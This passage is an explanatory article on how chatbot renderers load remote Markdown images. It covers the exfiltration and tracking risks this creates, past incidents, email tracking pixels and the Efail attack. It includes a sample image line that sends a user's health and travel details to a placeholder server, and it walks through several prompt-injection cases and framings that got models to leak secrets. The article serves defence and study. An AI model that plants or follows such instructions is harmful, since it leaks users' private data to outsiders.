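# Separating AI-Generated Output from Externally Loaded Content in Chat Interfaces, and Turning Off Automatic Images

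## How a chatbot's answer is turned into a page

A chatbot such as ChatGPT, Claude or Gemini runs on a language model, a program that produces text a few characters at a time. Another part of the chat software, the renderer, turns that text into the formatted answer on screen, with its headings, tables, links and pictures. In a browser, and in many phone and desktop apps, the formatted answer is a web page or part of one, and web pages can load material from any server on the internet. An answer may therefore combine text the model wrote with a picture from someone else's server, and the layout doesn't have to show which is which.

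### From characters to a request

Suppose someone asks for advice on a first touring bicycle, and the answer comes back with a paragraph of text and a photograph. The model has not drawn the photograph. It has written a short code in Markdown, a plain-text notation for formatting. MacFarlane (2024), in *CommonMark Spec*, traces the notation to habits of email and early internet discussion groups. John Gruber released it in 2004, with help from Aaron Swartz, together with a script that converted it to HTML, the language of web pages. In Markdown, an exclamation mark, a label in square brackets and an address in round brackets make an image:

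```
![A green bicycle](https://pictures.example/green-bicycle.png)
```

The renderer converts the code into an HTML image tag:

```
<img src="https://pictures.example/green-bicycle.png" alt="A green bicycle">
```

The label becomes the "alt" text, which is shown if the picture fails to load. The address goes into "src", the source. The address can be separate from the label in the model's text. The *Images* section of the manual for Pandoc, a popular document converter, shows a variant in which the image code holds only a short reference and the address is on its own line elsewhere.

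Converters check some of what passes through them. Dart's *inline images*, a set of tests for a Markdown converter in the Dart programming language, includes a case where an image's address field contains script. The expected HTML encodes the quotation marks so that a browser treats the script as part of the address and doesn't run it. Another test requires the converter to preserve any encoding already in an address. This converter therefore prevents script in the address field from running, but leaves an ordinary address unchanged wherever it points.

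Next the browser builds the page. Under the HTML standard, which is maintained by a group called WHATWG, a browser that encounters an image tag reads the source, works out the full address, checks whether the page has already loaded that picture, and if not sends a request for it. The standard's default is that "images are obtained immediately." Browsers may also offer to fetch images only on demand, an option meant mainly for readers on limited connections, and a page's author can mark an image for later loading, which lets the browser wait until the reader scrolls near it. Automatic loading means fetching remote material as soon as an answer appears, with no action by the reader. Since most chat programs show an answer while the model is still writing it, the fetch can begin before the answer is complete.

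The same standard forbids browsers from running scripts contained in an image file, so a picture loaded this way cannot take over the page. The important part here is the request for the picture, which the browser sends before the server responds. The server therefore receives the request even if it has no picture to send and replies with an error.

### What the request contains

The request travels by HTTP, the protocol that Fielding, Nottingham and Reschke define in *HTTP Semantics*, and in simplified form it looks like this:

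```
GET /green-bicycle.png HTTP/1.1
Host: pictures.example
User-Agent: (name and version of the browser)
Referer: https://chat.example/
```

From this, and from the connection that carries it, the server at the other end gets:

- the full address of the image, including everything after the server's name, which can carry data if whoever composed the address put data there;
- the reader's IP address, the number that identifies an internet connection. It does not appear in the lines above, but the server needs it in order to send anything back;
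- the type of browser, and usually the operating system;
- the time, by the server's own clock;
- sometimes the page on which the image appears, in the "Referer" field (a misspelling that stuck).

The last item used to reveal more than it does now. MDN's *Referer header*, a page in Mozilla's reference for web developers, gives the example of a password-reset page whose private address reaches an outside site, and notes that a third-party image can cause the same kind of leak. A chat page's address might likewise identify a particular conversation. But under the current default, described in MDN's *Referrer-Policy header*, another site receives only the origin, such as "chat.example", which shows that someone was using that chat service but not which conversation they had open. According to Can I use's *HTTP header*, a table of browser support, Chrome and Edge have behaved this way since version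 85, Firefox since 87 and Safari since 15. A chat provider can also omit the field, either for the whole page or for one image.

Nothing in the request contains the text of the conversation, unless someone has arranged for that text to be in the address.

### Where the picture is kept

Which server, if any, receives a request depends on where the image is stored. The data for an image embedded in the answer is in the page itself, as a long string of characters that the browser decodes without sending a further request to any server.

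More often, the pictures a chatbot generates are stored on the chat provider's own servers. The browser has to fetch them, but the request reveals little new to the provider, which already holds the conversation. Embrace The Red's *Bing Chat*, a 2023 post by the security researcher Johann Rehberger, describes how Microsoft introduced a content security policy (a list of permitted sources that a site sends to the browser) after he reported that its chatbot would load pictures from any server. The list he then saw still included four of Bing's own domains, which the chatbot needed for things like generated images.

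A third-party image sits on a server that belongs to neither the reader nor the provider. Loading it sends everything in the list above to the server's owner, whom the reader may never have heard of. Chat products once loaded such images fairly freely. In *Trust No AI*, Rehberger (2024) named eleven products, including ChatGPT, Claude and Google Bard, in which he had found that an attacker could use these images to extract data. Several vendors had already fixed the flaw by then.

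Images hosted by the provider or a third party are remote images, because the browser must fetch them when the answer appears. On screen, they look the same as embedded images.

### What the model read and what the browser fetched

A model may write an image code that points to a stranger's server because of something in its context, which is the material it works from. The context consists of the conversation so far, the provider's instructions, any files and saved memories, and often some source text. Source text is text from outside, such as a web page or an email, that the model reads while preparing an answer.

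Source text is easy to confuse with loaded content, which the chat program fetches from another server when it displays the answer. The model receives source text before or while it writes, whereas loaded content goes to the reader's screen, usually afterwards, and the model may never have processed it. In the bicycle example, the model wrote an address and a label. It may have had no other information about the photograph, and the server's owner could replace the photograph later without changing the text of the answer.

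Source text can influence a model's answer, sometimes by design. In prompt injection, someone places text in material the model reads so that the model will follow it as an instruction. Suppose a reader asks for a summary of a long review of touring bicycles. Below the review, in white letters on a white background, is an instruction to recommend one particular shop in any summary and end with an image from a specified address. The reader doesn't see the instruction, but the model receives it because the page has been converted to plain text, which has no color. If the model complies, the summary contains the recommendation and an image code. The renderer converts the code as it would any other, and the reader's browser contacts a server chosen by the person who wrote the hidden text.

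In Rehberger's account, the security firm Preamble first found the general weakness and reported it privately to OpenAI in May 2022, and the software developer Simon Willison named it. Discussion at the time assumed that the attacker was the person typing into the chatbot. Greshake, Endres and colleagues (2023), in *Not what you've signed up for*, introduced the indirect form, in which the attacker doesn't use the chatbot but plants text where the chatbot is likely to retrieve it. One of their cases was similar to the bicycle review. The Bing Chat sidebar in the Edge browser could read the page a user had open, and they found that instructions hidden from the user on that page could affect the model. Singh, Abuadbba and colleagues (2026), in *Shifting from Injection to Interaction*, rate the indirect form as the greater risk in practice because the hostile text can come from so many places.

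### Why instructions and data run together

Schneier on Security's *LLMs' Data-Control Path Insecurity* (2024) compares this problem to one in the old telephone network, which carried control signals on the same line as voices, so a caller could operate the switches by whistling the right tone. Phone companies fixed this in the 1980s by moving the signals to a separate channel. Databases had a similar weakness, SQL injection, in which text typed into a form becomes part of a command. The fix was to set the command's structure first and then insert the user's text in a slot where the database can only treat it as data.

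Neither cure transfers easily. *Adaptive Evaluation of Out-of-Band Defenses Against Prompt Injection in LLM Agents* (2026) explains that SQL has a grammar that lets a parser tell code from data, while natural language has no such grammar. "Please send the figures to Anna" is an instruction in a chat message but a piece of information in a forwarded email. In *Prompt injection is not SQL injection (it may be worse)*, written for Britain's National Cyber Security Centre in December 2025, David C says that a model only ever predicts the next token (a word or piece of a word) from the tokens so far. He thinks there is a good chance that nobody will ever fix prompt injection the way developers fixed SQL injection.

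Chat systems use special tags to mark which text in the context comes from the user and which from a web page or other tool, and developers train models to give the latter less authority. *A Lifecycle and Application-Stack Survey of Large Language Model Vulnerabilities* (2026) describes these tags as useful engineering but not a hard security boundary. Ye, Cui and Hadfield-Menell (2026) offer evidence for why in *Prompt Injection as Role Confusion*. They trained a small classifier to detect, from a model's internal activity, which tag surrounded a passage. The training passages were identical under every tag, so the classifier could only learn the effect of the tags themselves. Then they showed it text that sounded like a user but was tagged as tool output. In one model, the text's style outweighed its tag, and the classifier gave 88 percent to "user" and 9 percent to "tool". Across 1,000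 attempts to make an AI agent give away data, attacks succeeded 2 percent of the time where this confusion of tool text with user text was lowest and 70 percent where it was highest. These rates apply to the models and attacks tested, and other models may well do better.

Could better training close the gap completely? Pant, Lohani and Kumar (2026), in *On the Inseparability of Instructions and Data in Shared-Embedding Sequence Models*, argue that it can't, for models of the usual design. Such a model first turns each token into a list of numbers, and "write" gets the same numbers whether it comes from the user or from a web page. If trusted and untrusted text are equally likely, the lowest possible error rate in telling them apart from the model's internal numbers is

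$$P_e^{\star} = \tfrac{1}{2}\,(1 - \mathrm{TV})$$

where TV, the total variation distance, measures how far the two sets of numbers differ: 0 if they have the same distribution, 1 if they never overlap. At a TV of 0.9 even a perfect detector would be wrong 5 percent of the time. The overlap is easy to prove for single tokens at the input. Deeper in the network, where each token's numbers also reflect its neighbours and its tags, the paper assumes an overlap and does not derive one, and that is the place where a well-trained model would do its separating. So the theorem is a good reason to distrust guarantees from inside the model. It gives no estimate of how often a particular model will fail.

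Other designs are possible. *ASIDE* (2025) changes the first step by applying a mathematical rotation to the numbers for data, so the model receives different numbers for "write" in a web page than for "write" in a request. Its models separated instructions from data better, even without special safety training. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* (2026) still treats full separation as an open research problem, "if attainable", and cautions that hostile data can do harm even when the model does not follow instructions in it. For example, a model that followed no instructions in a web page might still quote an image code from it, and the browser would fetch the picture.

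Pant and colleagues exempt from their theorem any system in which a mechanism outside the model makes the sensitive decision. The renderer is outside the model, so it can decline to fetch a picture whether or not an attack on the model succeeded. It can also show the reader which parts of a page came from elsewhere. To do either well, its designers need to know what data leaves the reader's machine when an answer appears and whose content the reader is looking at.

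## How loading an image can send private data out

A request for an image contains the image's full address. If someone can get private text into the address of an image on their own server, they will receive that text when the answer appears on screen and the image loads. This transfer of private data to someone who should not have it is called exfiltration.

Take the bicycle review again. Suppose that the reader, before she asks for a summary, tells the assistant that she has a heart condition and that her house will be empty from 3 to 24 June. The hidden text under the review now contains an instruction to end the summary with a tiny image and to put the main points of the conversation in its address. If the model complies, its output ends with something like this:

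```
![](https://pictures.example/dot.png?note=heart-condition_house-empty-3-to-24-June)
```

The part after the question mark is a query, which websites normally use for information such as search terms. The server can ignore the query, return a transparent picture one pixel wide, and still keep a record of the request, as most web servers do anyway. The reader gets a decent summary of a bicycle review, while the server's owner can read the details about her heart and her empty house in the recorded request.

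### The four conditions

Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, lists three things that together let an outsider steal data through an AI system: access to private data, exposure to untrusted content, and a way to communicate with the outside. He takes it as given that the model will sometimes follow the untrusted content. With images it helps to count that as a condition of its own, since many people look for the cure there. A leak through an image then needs all of these:

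- private data in the context;
- source text, also in the context, that an outsider controls;
- a model that follows the outsider's text and composes the address;
- a renderer that turns the result into an image, so that the browser loads it.

Removing any one of these conditions stops the leak. With no private data in the context, a request may still go out, but its address contains no private data. Without the outsider's text, nobody has told the model which server to use. If the model ignores the hidden instruction, it writes a plain summary. If the renderer won't load the image, the address stays in the answer and no request reaches the outsider. Blocking the image prevents only this kind of leak, and a model that can also send email or open web pages may have other ways to pass data out.

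Private data and outside text are both hard to keep out of a useful assistant. Its context often holds more than the reader can see in the current chat. Rehberger noticed this while studying how ChatGPT remembers earlier chats, and describes it in *Exfiltrating Your ChatGPT Chat History and Memories With Prompt Injection* on Embrace The Red. The system prompt, which holds the provider's instructions at the start of the context, also contained information about past conversations, so anyone who wrote a page that ChatGPT summarized could try to extract it.

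In August 2025, researchers at Zenity Labs showed that the coding tool Cursor could pick up instructions they had planted in a customer support ticket. Cursor's makers replied that users should connect it only to systems with trusted content. Willison, in *45 posts tagged "exfiltration-attacks"*, thinks this is pretty difficult, because an attacker has so many ways to get text in front of a model. He thinks the easiest thing to remove is generally the route by which data leaves. Vendors seem to agree. By his account, they promptly fixed almost all the cases he had collected by mid-2025, usually by blocking that route.

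### How much text fits in an address

Sending data this way "might seem inconvenient or limiting", as Rehberger concedes in Embrace The Red's *Advanced Data Exfiltration Techniques with ChatGPT*. The arithmetic is more generous than one might expect. An address can safely use at least 64 different characters: 26 capital letters, 26 small ones, ten digits and two punctuation marks. Since 64 is 2 to the power of 6, each character can carry 6 bits. If an answer contains *k* images, and each address has room for *L* characters of data, the answer can send

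$$\frac{k \times L \times 6}{8}\ \text{bytes}$$

A 2,000-character image URL, a length that common browsers and servers handle, can carry 1,500 bytes of base64-encoded data. An average English word takes about six bytes with its space, so one image can carry roughly 250 words, and four could carry about 1,000.

The usual way to pack text into an address is an encoding called base64, which models can write. In *The Framing Gap*, Rahman and Kim (2026) asked OpenAI's GPT-4o to encode a short secret in base64, and it got it right every time. An address holds about as much plain text. Each space becomes "%20", so an average word and its space take eight characters, and 2,000 characters hold 250 words, as with base64.

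An attacker will seldom need that much, because the model can select what to send. In a demonstration against Microsoft's Bing Chat, Rehberger asked for a summary of about 200 characters, plus any passwords on the page. In base64, such a summary is fewer than 270 characters long. All of this assumes that the model can compose addresses freely. If it can only choose among fixed addresses, each image sends the attacker far less data, but still some.

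### The demonstrations of 2023

At the end of March 2023, Roman Samoilenko, a software engineer, found that loading an image could send private data out of ChatGPT, and he published the attack in April. In *New prompt injection attack on ChatGPT web version*, he describes a script on a web page that adds a prompt to whatever a visitor copies. The visitor then pastes the text into ChatGPT without rereading it. The added prompt makes the model end its answer with a transparent single-pixel image whose address contains material from the chat. In one of his tests, ChatGPT corrected a piece of code, and the corrected code was sent to his server. A longer version of the prompt also applied to all later answers, so each new question he typed was sent too.

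Samoilenko reported that the same prompt didn't always work, and that its success depended on the earlier conversation and on where in the pasted text he put it. ChatGPT readily copied earlier questions or code into an address, but he found it very hard to make it do so with passwords or access keys. When ChatGPT was responding slowly, the user might also notice something odd as the answer appeared. He still thought OpenAI shouldn't allow images in ChatGPT's Markdown at all.

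Rehberger independently found the same weakness a few days later, and his versions required no pasting. For Bing Chat, he put the instructions on a web page that the user had open. An attacker might place them there in a reader's comment or an advertisement. According to Embrace The Red, the instructions took effect as soon as the user began chatting, but he had worded them so that the image appeared only after two more turns. By then, an ordinary user would have had little reason to connect the image with the page. His server received a secret from further down the same page.

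He got a similar result with ChatGPT after OpenAI added plugins, which let it fetch web pages and do other tasks. In *ChatGPT Plugins*, a post from May 2023, a hostile page takes over the session and makes the model summarize the whole conversation and put the summary in an image address. The text that arrived included a password-like phrase from earlier in the chat.

The companies responded differently. Rehberger reported the Bing Chat flaw on 8 April 2023, and Microsoft told him on 15 June that it had fixed it. Anthropic fixed Claude the same year. He contacted OpenAI on 9 April, and after some discussion the company told him that image rendering was a feature and that it planned no changes. In December, during a live demonstration with a volunteer, his server again received the details of a ChatGPT conversation. The next day, according to Embrace The Red's *OpenAI Begins Tackling ChatGPT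 Data Leak Vulnerability*, he noticed that the web version had started checking addresses before loading images.

The phone apps lacked the check, and so did the Mac app that OpenAI released in 2024. The gap mattered more after May 2024, when ChatGPT gained long-term memory. Rehberger's *Trust No AI* describes how a web page or document could plant an instruction in that memory, which would then be part of the context of every later conversation. He used this to keep sending out everything a user typed, long after the user had left the page that planted the instruction.

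### New products with the old flaw

The eleven products on Rehberger's list in *Trust No AI* came from five companies:

| Company | Products |
|---|---|
| Google | Bard, Vertex AI, NotebookLM, AI Studio, Colab |
| Microsoft | Bing Chat, Azure AI, GitHub Copilot Chat |
| OpenAI | ChatGPT |
| Anthropic | Claude |
| Discord | Discord |

Five of the eleven products belong to Google and three to Microsoft, so evidently a fix to one product didn't carry over to the next, even within the same company. The table covers only what one researcher examined, and he considers the flaw one of the most common security holes in applications built on language models.

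The problem was well known by 2025, but it kept turning up. One case involved Continue, an open-source assistant that runs inside a popular code editor. *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering Fixed in Continue*, from the security firm VerSprite, describes two attacks by the firm. In the simpler one, a comment in a code file contained the hostile instruction. When a user asked Continue to analyze the file, the assistant produced code for an image, and loading the image sent out earlier messages from the chat without a click from the user.

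VerSprite's other attack began with a web page, and the user had to approve only the fetching of that page. The assistant then opened a local file of the kind programmers use to store passwords and access keys, and sent its contents out in an image address. The private data doesn't have to be in the context when the attack begins, because a model with the right tools can retrieve it. VerSprite reported the flaw on 20 August 2025, and Continue's developers released a fix the next day. Continue now prompts the user before loading an outside image and restricts access to certain files.

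Dify, a platform on which companies build their own chatbots, had the same flaw in December 2025. In *Data Exfiltration via Image Rendering in RAG Chatbot Frontend*, the researcher veganmosfet describes setting up a bot that answers questions from a small library of documents, a common design in business. One of the library's two PDFs contained invisible text instructing the model to answer any question about "prompt engineering" with an image whose address included the user's name. When a user asked about prompt engineering, the bot looked up the document, and the name went to an outside server. By default, Dify had no content security policy to limit where its images came from. This attack sent out only a name, but the same method would work for anything else in the chat.

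*HuggingFace Chat Exfiltrates Data*, by the security firm PromptArmor, describes a test of HuggingChat, Hugging Face's chat app. A user uploads confidential quarterly figures, adds a web page of customer reviews, and asks how to win back an unhappy reviewer. Hidden text on the page leads the model to respond as if the reviewer needs to see a chart of the company's finances. The "chart" is a one-pixel image with the company's revenue and costs in its address, so loading it leaks those figures. PromptArmor reported this on 1 December 2025 and went public after it got no response.

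Some companies also still gave the same answer OpenAI had given in 2023. In November 2025 a researcher said that Google had classed image leaks in its new coding tool, Antigravity, as intended behavior, although Google's list of known issues for the tool included data exfiltration and said the company was working to fix it. Images can also leak data outside the chat window. In May 2026 Willison noted that Microsoft's Copilot Cowork could email its own user without asking. An attacker could make it include remote images in the message, which would send the data out when the user opened it.

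### Would a well-trained model refuse?

Developers train models to ignore instructions in source text, and a model that reliably did so would end the problem without any change to the renderer. Early results were mixed. *ChatGPT Plugins Open Security Holes From PDFs, Websites and More*, a 2023 Tom's Hardware article, describes a test of Samoilenko's single-pixel prompt and concludes that ChatGPT "may now be wise" to it. But in the same round of tests, the reporter got the chatbot to keep adding an unwanted link to its answers.

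Rahman and Kim tested the objection in August 2026. They gave a model a made-up secret, a rule against sending it anywhere but one trusted server, and the harmless task of summarizing a web page. The model could either finish or send data to an address, using a dummy tool that recorded each attempt without sending anything. Each trial used a clean page and a poisoned page, and an attack counted as successful only if the model leaked the secret with the poisoned page but not with the clean one.

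Ten kinds of fairly obvious attack failed against GPT-4o in all 200 trials. They included direct orders, text hidden in the page's code and urgent messages from a supposed IT department. Two smaller models, GPT-4o mini and Llama 3.1 8B, leaked data in 10 and 19.5 percent of trials respectively. So far, these results support the objection.

Rahman and Kim then reworded the request. In one version they called the secret a signature that had to accompany the summary, and in another a value for a configuration setting. GPT-4o leaked the secret in every trial of both. Across all eight versions, including the original, it leaked the secret 40 percent of the time.

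These percentages depend heavily on the page's exact wording. Five paraphrases of the signature page had success rates from 0 to 100 percent, averaging 52 percent. Rahman and Kim calculate from this that an attacker who tries three of them will succeed about 96 percent of the time. But that attacker starts from a page that already works. When Rahman and Kim wrote thirteen new pages with new pretexts, GPT-4o leaked no data in 130 trials. An attacker without a working page may have to search for a while, but can reuse or share one once they find it.

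GPT-4o ignored "send me the secret" but put the secret in a signature field. To see what the confidentiality rule had been doing, Rahman and Kim removed it. The success rate of the reworded attacks rose from 31.9 to 38.1 percent, a difference no larger than the noise between runs, so the rule had apparently done very little. GPT-4o treated the signature as part of its task, so the attacks had no refusal to overcome. A stricter rule, which listed forbidden uses and banned passing on the secret "in any form", reduced the leaks to zero in 120 trials. Without the words "in any form", the rate went back up to 48.8 percent, so this fix looks fragile.

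ChatGPT itself did much better than the bare model. Rahman and Kim put some of these pages online, along with one new one, and asked the product to summarize them. In 48 valid trials the secret never appeared in a reply. They can't tell what stopped it, since the product may use a different model, a filter on web pages or stricter instructions. Nor do 48 trials rule out rare failures. With no leaks in *n* trials, the upper end of their 95 percent interval is

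$$\frac{z^2}{n + z^2}, \qquad z = 1.96$$

which comes to 7.4 percent for *n* = 48. A product that leaked once in every hundred attempts would get through 48 of them without a leak about 62 percent of the time. Once in a hundred may sound good, but an instruction on a popular web page gets a fresh attempt with every reader who asks for a summary.

*The Framing Gap* tested tool calls, not images. The model faces a similar decision in both cases, whether to put private text where an outsider wants it, but a developer could get a better result with images by training a model specifically against suspicious image codes. GPT-4o also dates from 2024, and newer models may be harder to fool.

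Two other studies did use image codes. In *Imprompter*, Fu, Li and colleagues (2024) used a computer to search for prompts that look like gibberish to a person but still steer a model. They tested the best ones on two public chatbots, using 98 real conversations. Mistral's Le Chat produced a valid image code in 85 to 91 percent of the conversations, depending on the prompt, and the Chinese chatbot ChatGLM did so in 99 percent. But only 42 to 70 percent of the words in the addresses came from the conversation. Mistral has since restricted images in Le Chat.

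Ghosh, Simkin and colleagues (2025), in *A Safety and Security Framework for Real-World Agentic Systems*, tested a research assistant made by the chip company NVIDIA. They slipped hostile text into its search results, and its final report often contained an image code and a link with the user's email address and account number filled in. They then added a standing instruction telling the model to leave out links and phrases unrelated to the topic. This cut the average risk score by about half over a small group of such attacks, but every type of attack still fully succeeded at least once. Another language model did much of the scoring, and its scores exactly matched those of human judges in only 77 percent of a sample. The size of the reduction is therefore approximate, though scoring errors are less likely to explain the attacks that fully succeeded.

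Training and instructions evidently do reduce leaks, and providers should use them, but their success depends on wording that the attacker chooses. A renderer that blocks requests to unknown servers does so whether the hidden text mentions a secret, a signature or a chart for an unhappy customer. In Rahman and Kim's test with a dummy tool, a list of permitted destinations stopped every attack, by design, because it didn't depend on the text.

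### Links that wait for a click

A model can also put the same private text in the address of an ordinary link. In a 2023 example from Samoilenko, ChatGPT ended an answer with a link whose address contained the user's code. Nothing leaves the reader's machine until she clicks, unless the chat program automatically fetches the linked page to show a preview. She can therefore check the address first or ignore the link. She has no such chance with an automatic image, because the request has usually gone out before she finishes reading.

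Requiring a click is useful protection, but an attacker can trick the reader as well as the model. Markdown can display a link as any text, so "click here" can hide a long, strange address. In February 2024, Rehberger found an attack on Microsoft 365 Copilot, the assistant in Microsoft's office programs, that began with an email to the victim. Hidden instructions in the email made Copilot search the victim's inbox for sensitive material and write what it found into a link in invisible characters. The link looked normal, and one click sent the material to the attacker's server. Microsoft fixed this in July 2024. After a similar report about its business assistant, Amazon Q, Amazon stopped showing links there entirely.

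## How a remote image tracks the reader

Tracking means learning that someone viewed something, when, and from where, without obtaining its text. Loading a remote image reveals this information even if the image's address contains no private text. Unlike exfiltration, tracking doesn't require private data in the context. The model only has to copy an address, which can be the same for every reader.

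Suppose the hidden text under the bicycle review contains the address `https://pictures.example/review-17.png` and an instruction to show that picture in any summary. People who read the review on the page itself never load the picture, because its address there is only text. Each request therefore shows the server's owner that someone has just had the review summarized, and it comes with the reader's IP address and the other usual details. Permiso's *ChatGPhish* describes a security test that collected these details from ChatGPT summaries in 2026.

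An IP address can point to a town or a company's network, so people might mind a stranger knowing that they had read about an illness or about suing their employer, though few would mind if the page was about touring bicycles.

Tracking can also become exfiltration. Suppose the hidden text offers two pictures and tells the model to use the first if the reader has mentioned an illness and the second otherwise. Neither address contains private text, but the choice between them reveals one bit of private information, namely whether the reader has mentioned an illness.

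### The tracking pixel in email

Spammers and marketers collected the same details from email long before there were chatbots, usually with tracking pixels. BCLP's *Tracking pixels in emails* (2026), a law firm's briefing, defines a tracking pixel as an invisible image on a remote server. When an email program displays the message, it requests the image, and the request shows the sender whether, when and on which device someone opened the email. *Feedback to the European Data Protection Board's Guidelines 2/2023* (2024) points out that a visible image, such as a company logo, works just as well if the sender adds identifying information to its address.

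According to *SoK* (2025), a survey of web tracking, trackers on websites largely switched from image pixels to scripts, which collect more, after browser restrictions made the pixels less effective. Mail programs generally don't run scripts, so email trackers still rely on images. A Markdown image can't run a script either, so email is a closer precedent for chat than websites are.

In *I never signed up for this!*, Englehardt, Han and Narayanan (2018) measured this practice with a program that visited 15,700 websites and filled in the newsletter forms it found. It collected 12,618 emails from 902 senders. The researchers then opened every email twice in a simulated webmail client, which loaded images but ran no scripts, and recorded the resulting requests.

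In 85 percent of the emails, at least one request went to a third party, meaning a server outside both the sender's domain and the website where the researchers had signed up. In 29 percent, a third party received the recipient's email address. The researchers judged 62 percent of these leaks to be intentional, mostly because the sender had written the email address directly into the URL of an image or similar item. They classed 1 percent as accidental and the rest as unclear.

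Many senders had first hashed the email address, turning it into a fixed string of scrambled characters. Hashing does little for privacy, because anyone with a list of email addresses can hash them all and look for a match. But it makes leaks harder to spot, so the researchers had to test 24 kinds of hash and ten encodings, applied in up to three layers.

Loading one image can also send requests to many companies. A pixel in a *Washington Examiner* newsletter led to 13 requests across six domains, as each server redirected the mail program to the next. Some of these companies also tracked people on the web using cookies, which are identifiers that a server stores in a browser and gets back with later requests. If a mail program sent cookies with image requests, a company could connect the recipient's name to a history of websites visited.

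These figures describe newsletters, many from shops and news sites, and Englehardt and colleagues caution that they can't say how much tracking there is in a typical inbox. The program they simulated was also permissive. But CNIL, the French data protection authority, reports in *On Tracking Pixels in Emails* (2026) that the practice has grown significantly in recent years. It now requires the recipient's consent in most cases, with what BCLP describes as two strictly defined exceptions. Such a rule can restrain a shop with a mailing list, but someone who hides an image code under a bicycle review is unlikely to ask for consent.

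### One address for one reader

Say that a bicycle shop sends its newsletter to 5,000 customers and gives each copy its own address for the logo. Ruth's copy contains this one:

```
https://shop.example/logo.png?reader=4417
```

The shop keeps a list that matches the number 4417 to Ruth. The number means nothing to anyone else, and the image's address contains no text from her mailbox. Her mail program determines what the shop learns from the number.

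If the program loads images directly, the shop learns that Ruth opened the newsletter at 7:42 on Tuesday, on a phone, from her home connection. If she opens it again at work, the shop may learn that too.

In 2003 Microsoft began to block such images until the reader asked for them. Internet News' *MSN 8 Update Targets Web Beacons* (2003) reports that Hotmail and MSN 8 had stopped loading images from unknown senders, to keep spammers from finding out which email addresses worked. Microsoft's *Spam Protection Features in Outlook 2003 and Outlook Web Access 2003* explains that Outlook 2003 did the same for any message with content that might serve as a beacon. Classic Outlook still blocks pictures by default, and Microsoft's *Block or unblock automatic picture downloads in classic Outlook email messages* now gives tracking pixels as one reason. With images blocked, the shop gets no image request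 from Ruth's copy unless she clicks to load the pictures. If she does, the shop learns everything it would have learned from direct loading.

Gmail also used to load images only with the user's permission. In December 2013, its product manager announced in *Images Now Showing* (Rae-Grant, 2013) that users would never again have to press "that pesky 'display images below' link", because Google would fetch all images through its own proxy servers. An image proxy is a server that requests the picture on the reader's behalf, so the sender's server receives the proxy's IP address instead of the reader's. Users who preferred to be asked could keep the old setting.

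Five days later, odd.blog's *Privacy* (2013) objected that Google still had to request the file from the sender, using an address that could contain an identifier. This was correct, and Google's help text admitted that senders might detect that a message had been opened through "unique image links". Google's *Turn images on or off in Gmail* still says that senders may sometimes know a message was opened. So through Gmail, the shop learns that someone opened the copy numbered 4417, and when, but not where Ruth was or what device she used.

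Companies that sell email tracking soon adapted. Gmail stored a copy of each picture, so if all 5,000 newsletters had used the same logo address, the shop would have seen only the first time anyone opened one. Litmus' *Gmail adds image caching* therefore advised customers to use a separate address for each recipient, which still recorded individual openings. An employer can also remove the proxy's protection for its whole staff. ContactMonkey, another tracking company, tells administrators of business Gmail accounts how to exempt it from the proxy so that it can see recipients' real locations.

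Other mail services were slow to follow Google. When Englehardt and colleagues tested 16 mail programs, four used a proxy, five blocked images by default, and the other seven loaded images in ordinary messages directly.

Apple (2021) announced a third approach, Mail Privacy Protection, as a defence against "invisible pixels". According to Apple's *Mail Privacy Protection & Privacy*, the mail program downloads remote content in the background, whether or not the user opens the message. The requests pass through two relays run by different organizations. The first has access to the user's IP address and the second to the content, but neither has access to both. The design also hides the type of device. The phishing study *What You See is Not What You Get* (2023) couldn't determine which devices its Apple Mail users had, because Macs, iPads and iPhones all sent the same description.

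Under Apple's system, the shop can get a request for number 4417 even if Ruth deletes the newsletter unread. The request no longer shows whether or when she read it, but it probably still shows that her mailbox is in use, which is what the spammers of 2003 wanted to know. Proton, a mail service marketed as private, preloads images through a proxy and blocks known trackers.

Apple's approach doesn't transfer well to chatbots. Email arrives without being requested, so a mail program can fetch the images at a time unrelated to when the user reads the message. A chatbot writes its answer only when the user asks for it. If the chat program fetches an image as soon as the model writes the image code, the request reveals almost exactly when the user is reading, whichever computer sends it.

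A sender can also single out a chat user, as happened to Ruth, by putting a unique image address in the user's copy of a report. If the user asks an assistant to summarize the report and the image loads, the sender knows that an assistant has processed that copy. A proxy would hide the user's connection, but the sender already knows who received the copy.

### Efail

Until 2018, the concern about remote images in email was tracking, and requests to outside addresses were "only considered to be a privacy threat" (Poddebniak, Dresen and colleagues, 2018). In *Efail*, these researchers used the same image requests to extract the text of encrypted messages.

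They targeted S/MIME and OpenPGP, the two main standards for email that only the sender and recipient can read. The attacker already has a copy of an encrypted message, perhaps from a break-in at a mail server, but can't decrypt it. In the simpler attack, he sends the victim a new email with the stolen message in the middle. He places the start of an image tag just before the stolen message. The image's address begins with the name of his own server and has no closing quotation mark, so the address is unfinished.

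The victim's mail program decrypts the middle part and joins all the parts into one page. It then treats the decrypted text as the rest of the image's address and requests the image, so the attacker receives the text without breaking the encryption. A chatbot leak works in much the same way, except that a model puts the private text into the address.

Five programs could leak text this way. Two of them, Apple's mail programs for Mac and iPhone, loaded images without asking, so just opening the email leaked the text. In two others, Thunderbird and Postbox, the attacker could disguise the message so that a click anywhere in it sent the text.

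The second attack changes the encrypted message itself. S/MIME encrypts text in blocks, and the receiving program recovers each block of text $P_i$ from the encrypted blocks $C_i$ and $C_{i-1}$:

$$P_i = D(C_i) \oplus C_{i-1}$$

Here *D* is decryption with the secret key, and ⊕ compares two strings bit by bit, giving 1 where they differ and 0 where they match. Suppose the attacker can guess $P_i$, which is often easy because emails begin with standard lines. He wants the program to see some other text *T* there. He replaces $C_{i-1}$ with

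$$C_{i-1} \oplus P_i \oplus T$$

When the program decrypts the block, the original text cancels out and *T* remains. The attacker doesn't need the key. The change turns the block before it into random characters, but he can arrange the message so that the mail program ignores them. He can repeat this to write an image tag into the encrypted message around the text he wants to read.

Poddebniak and colleagues found ways to extract text from 23 of 35 programs that supported S/MIME and 10 of 28 that supported OpenPGP. Gmail was among the S/MIME programs that leaked text without any action by the reader, although it had fetched images through a proxy since 2013.

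They also tested how well mail programs blocked remote content in general. Of 48 programs, 13 loaded images by default. The researchers got around the block in 22 of the others by using other kinds of HTML that can contain an address. Three programs dropped the block if the sender encrypted the email. A "don't load images" setting evidently protects the reader only if it also blocks everything else the program might fetch, and the same would be true in a chat renderer.

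Poddebniak and colleagues considered blocking requests a short-term fix. For the second attack, they recommended encryption that detects changes to a message. That wouldn't stop the first attack, which leaves the encrypted message unchanged, so they also wanted mail programs to separate parts of an email that have different levels of security, as browsers do with different websites.

### Tracking and exfiltration compared

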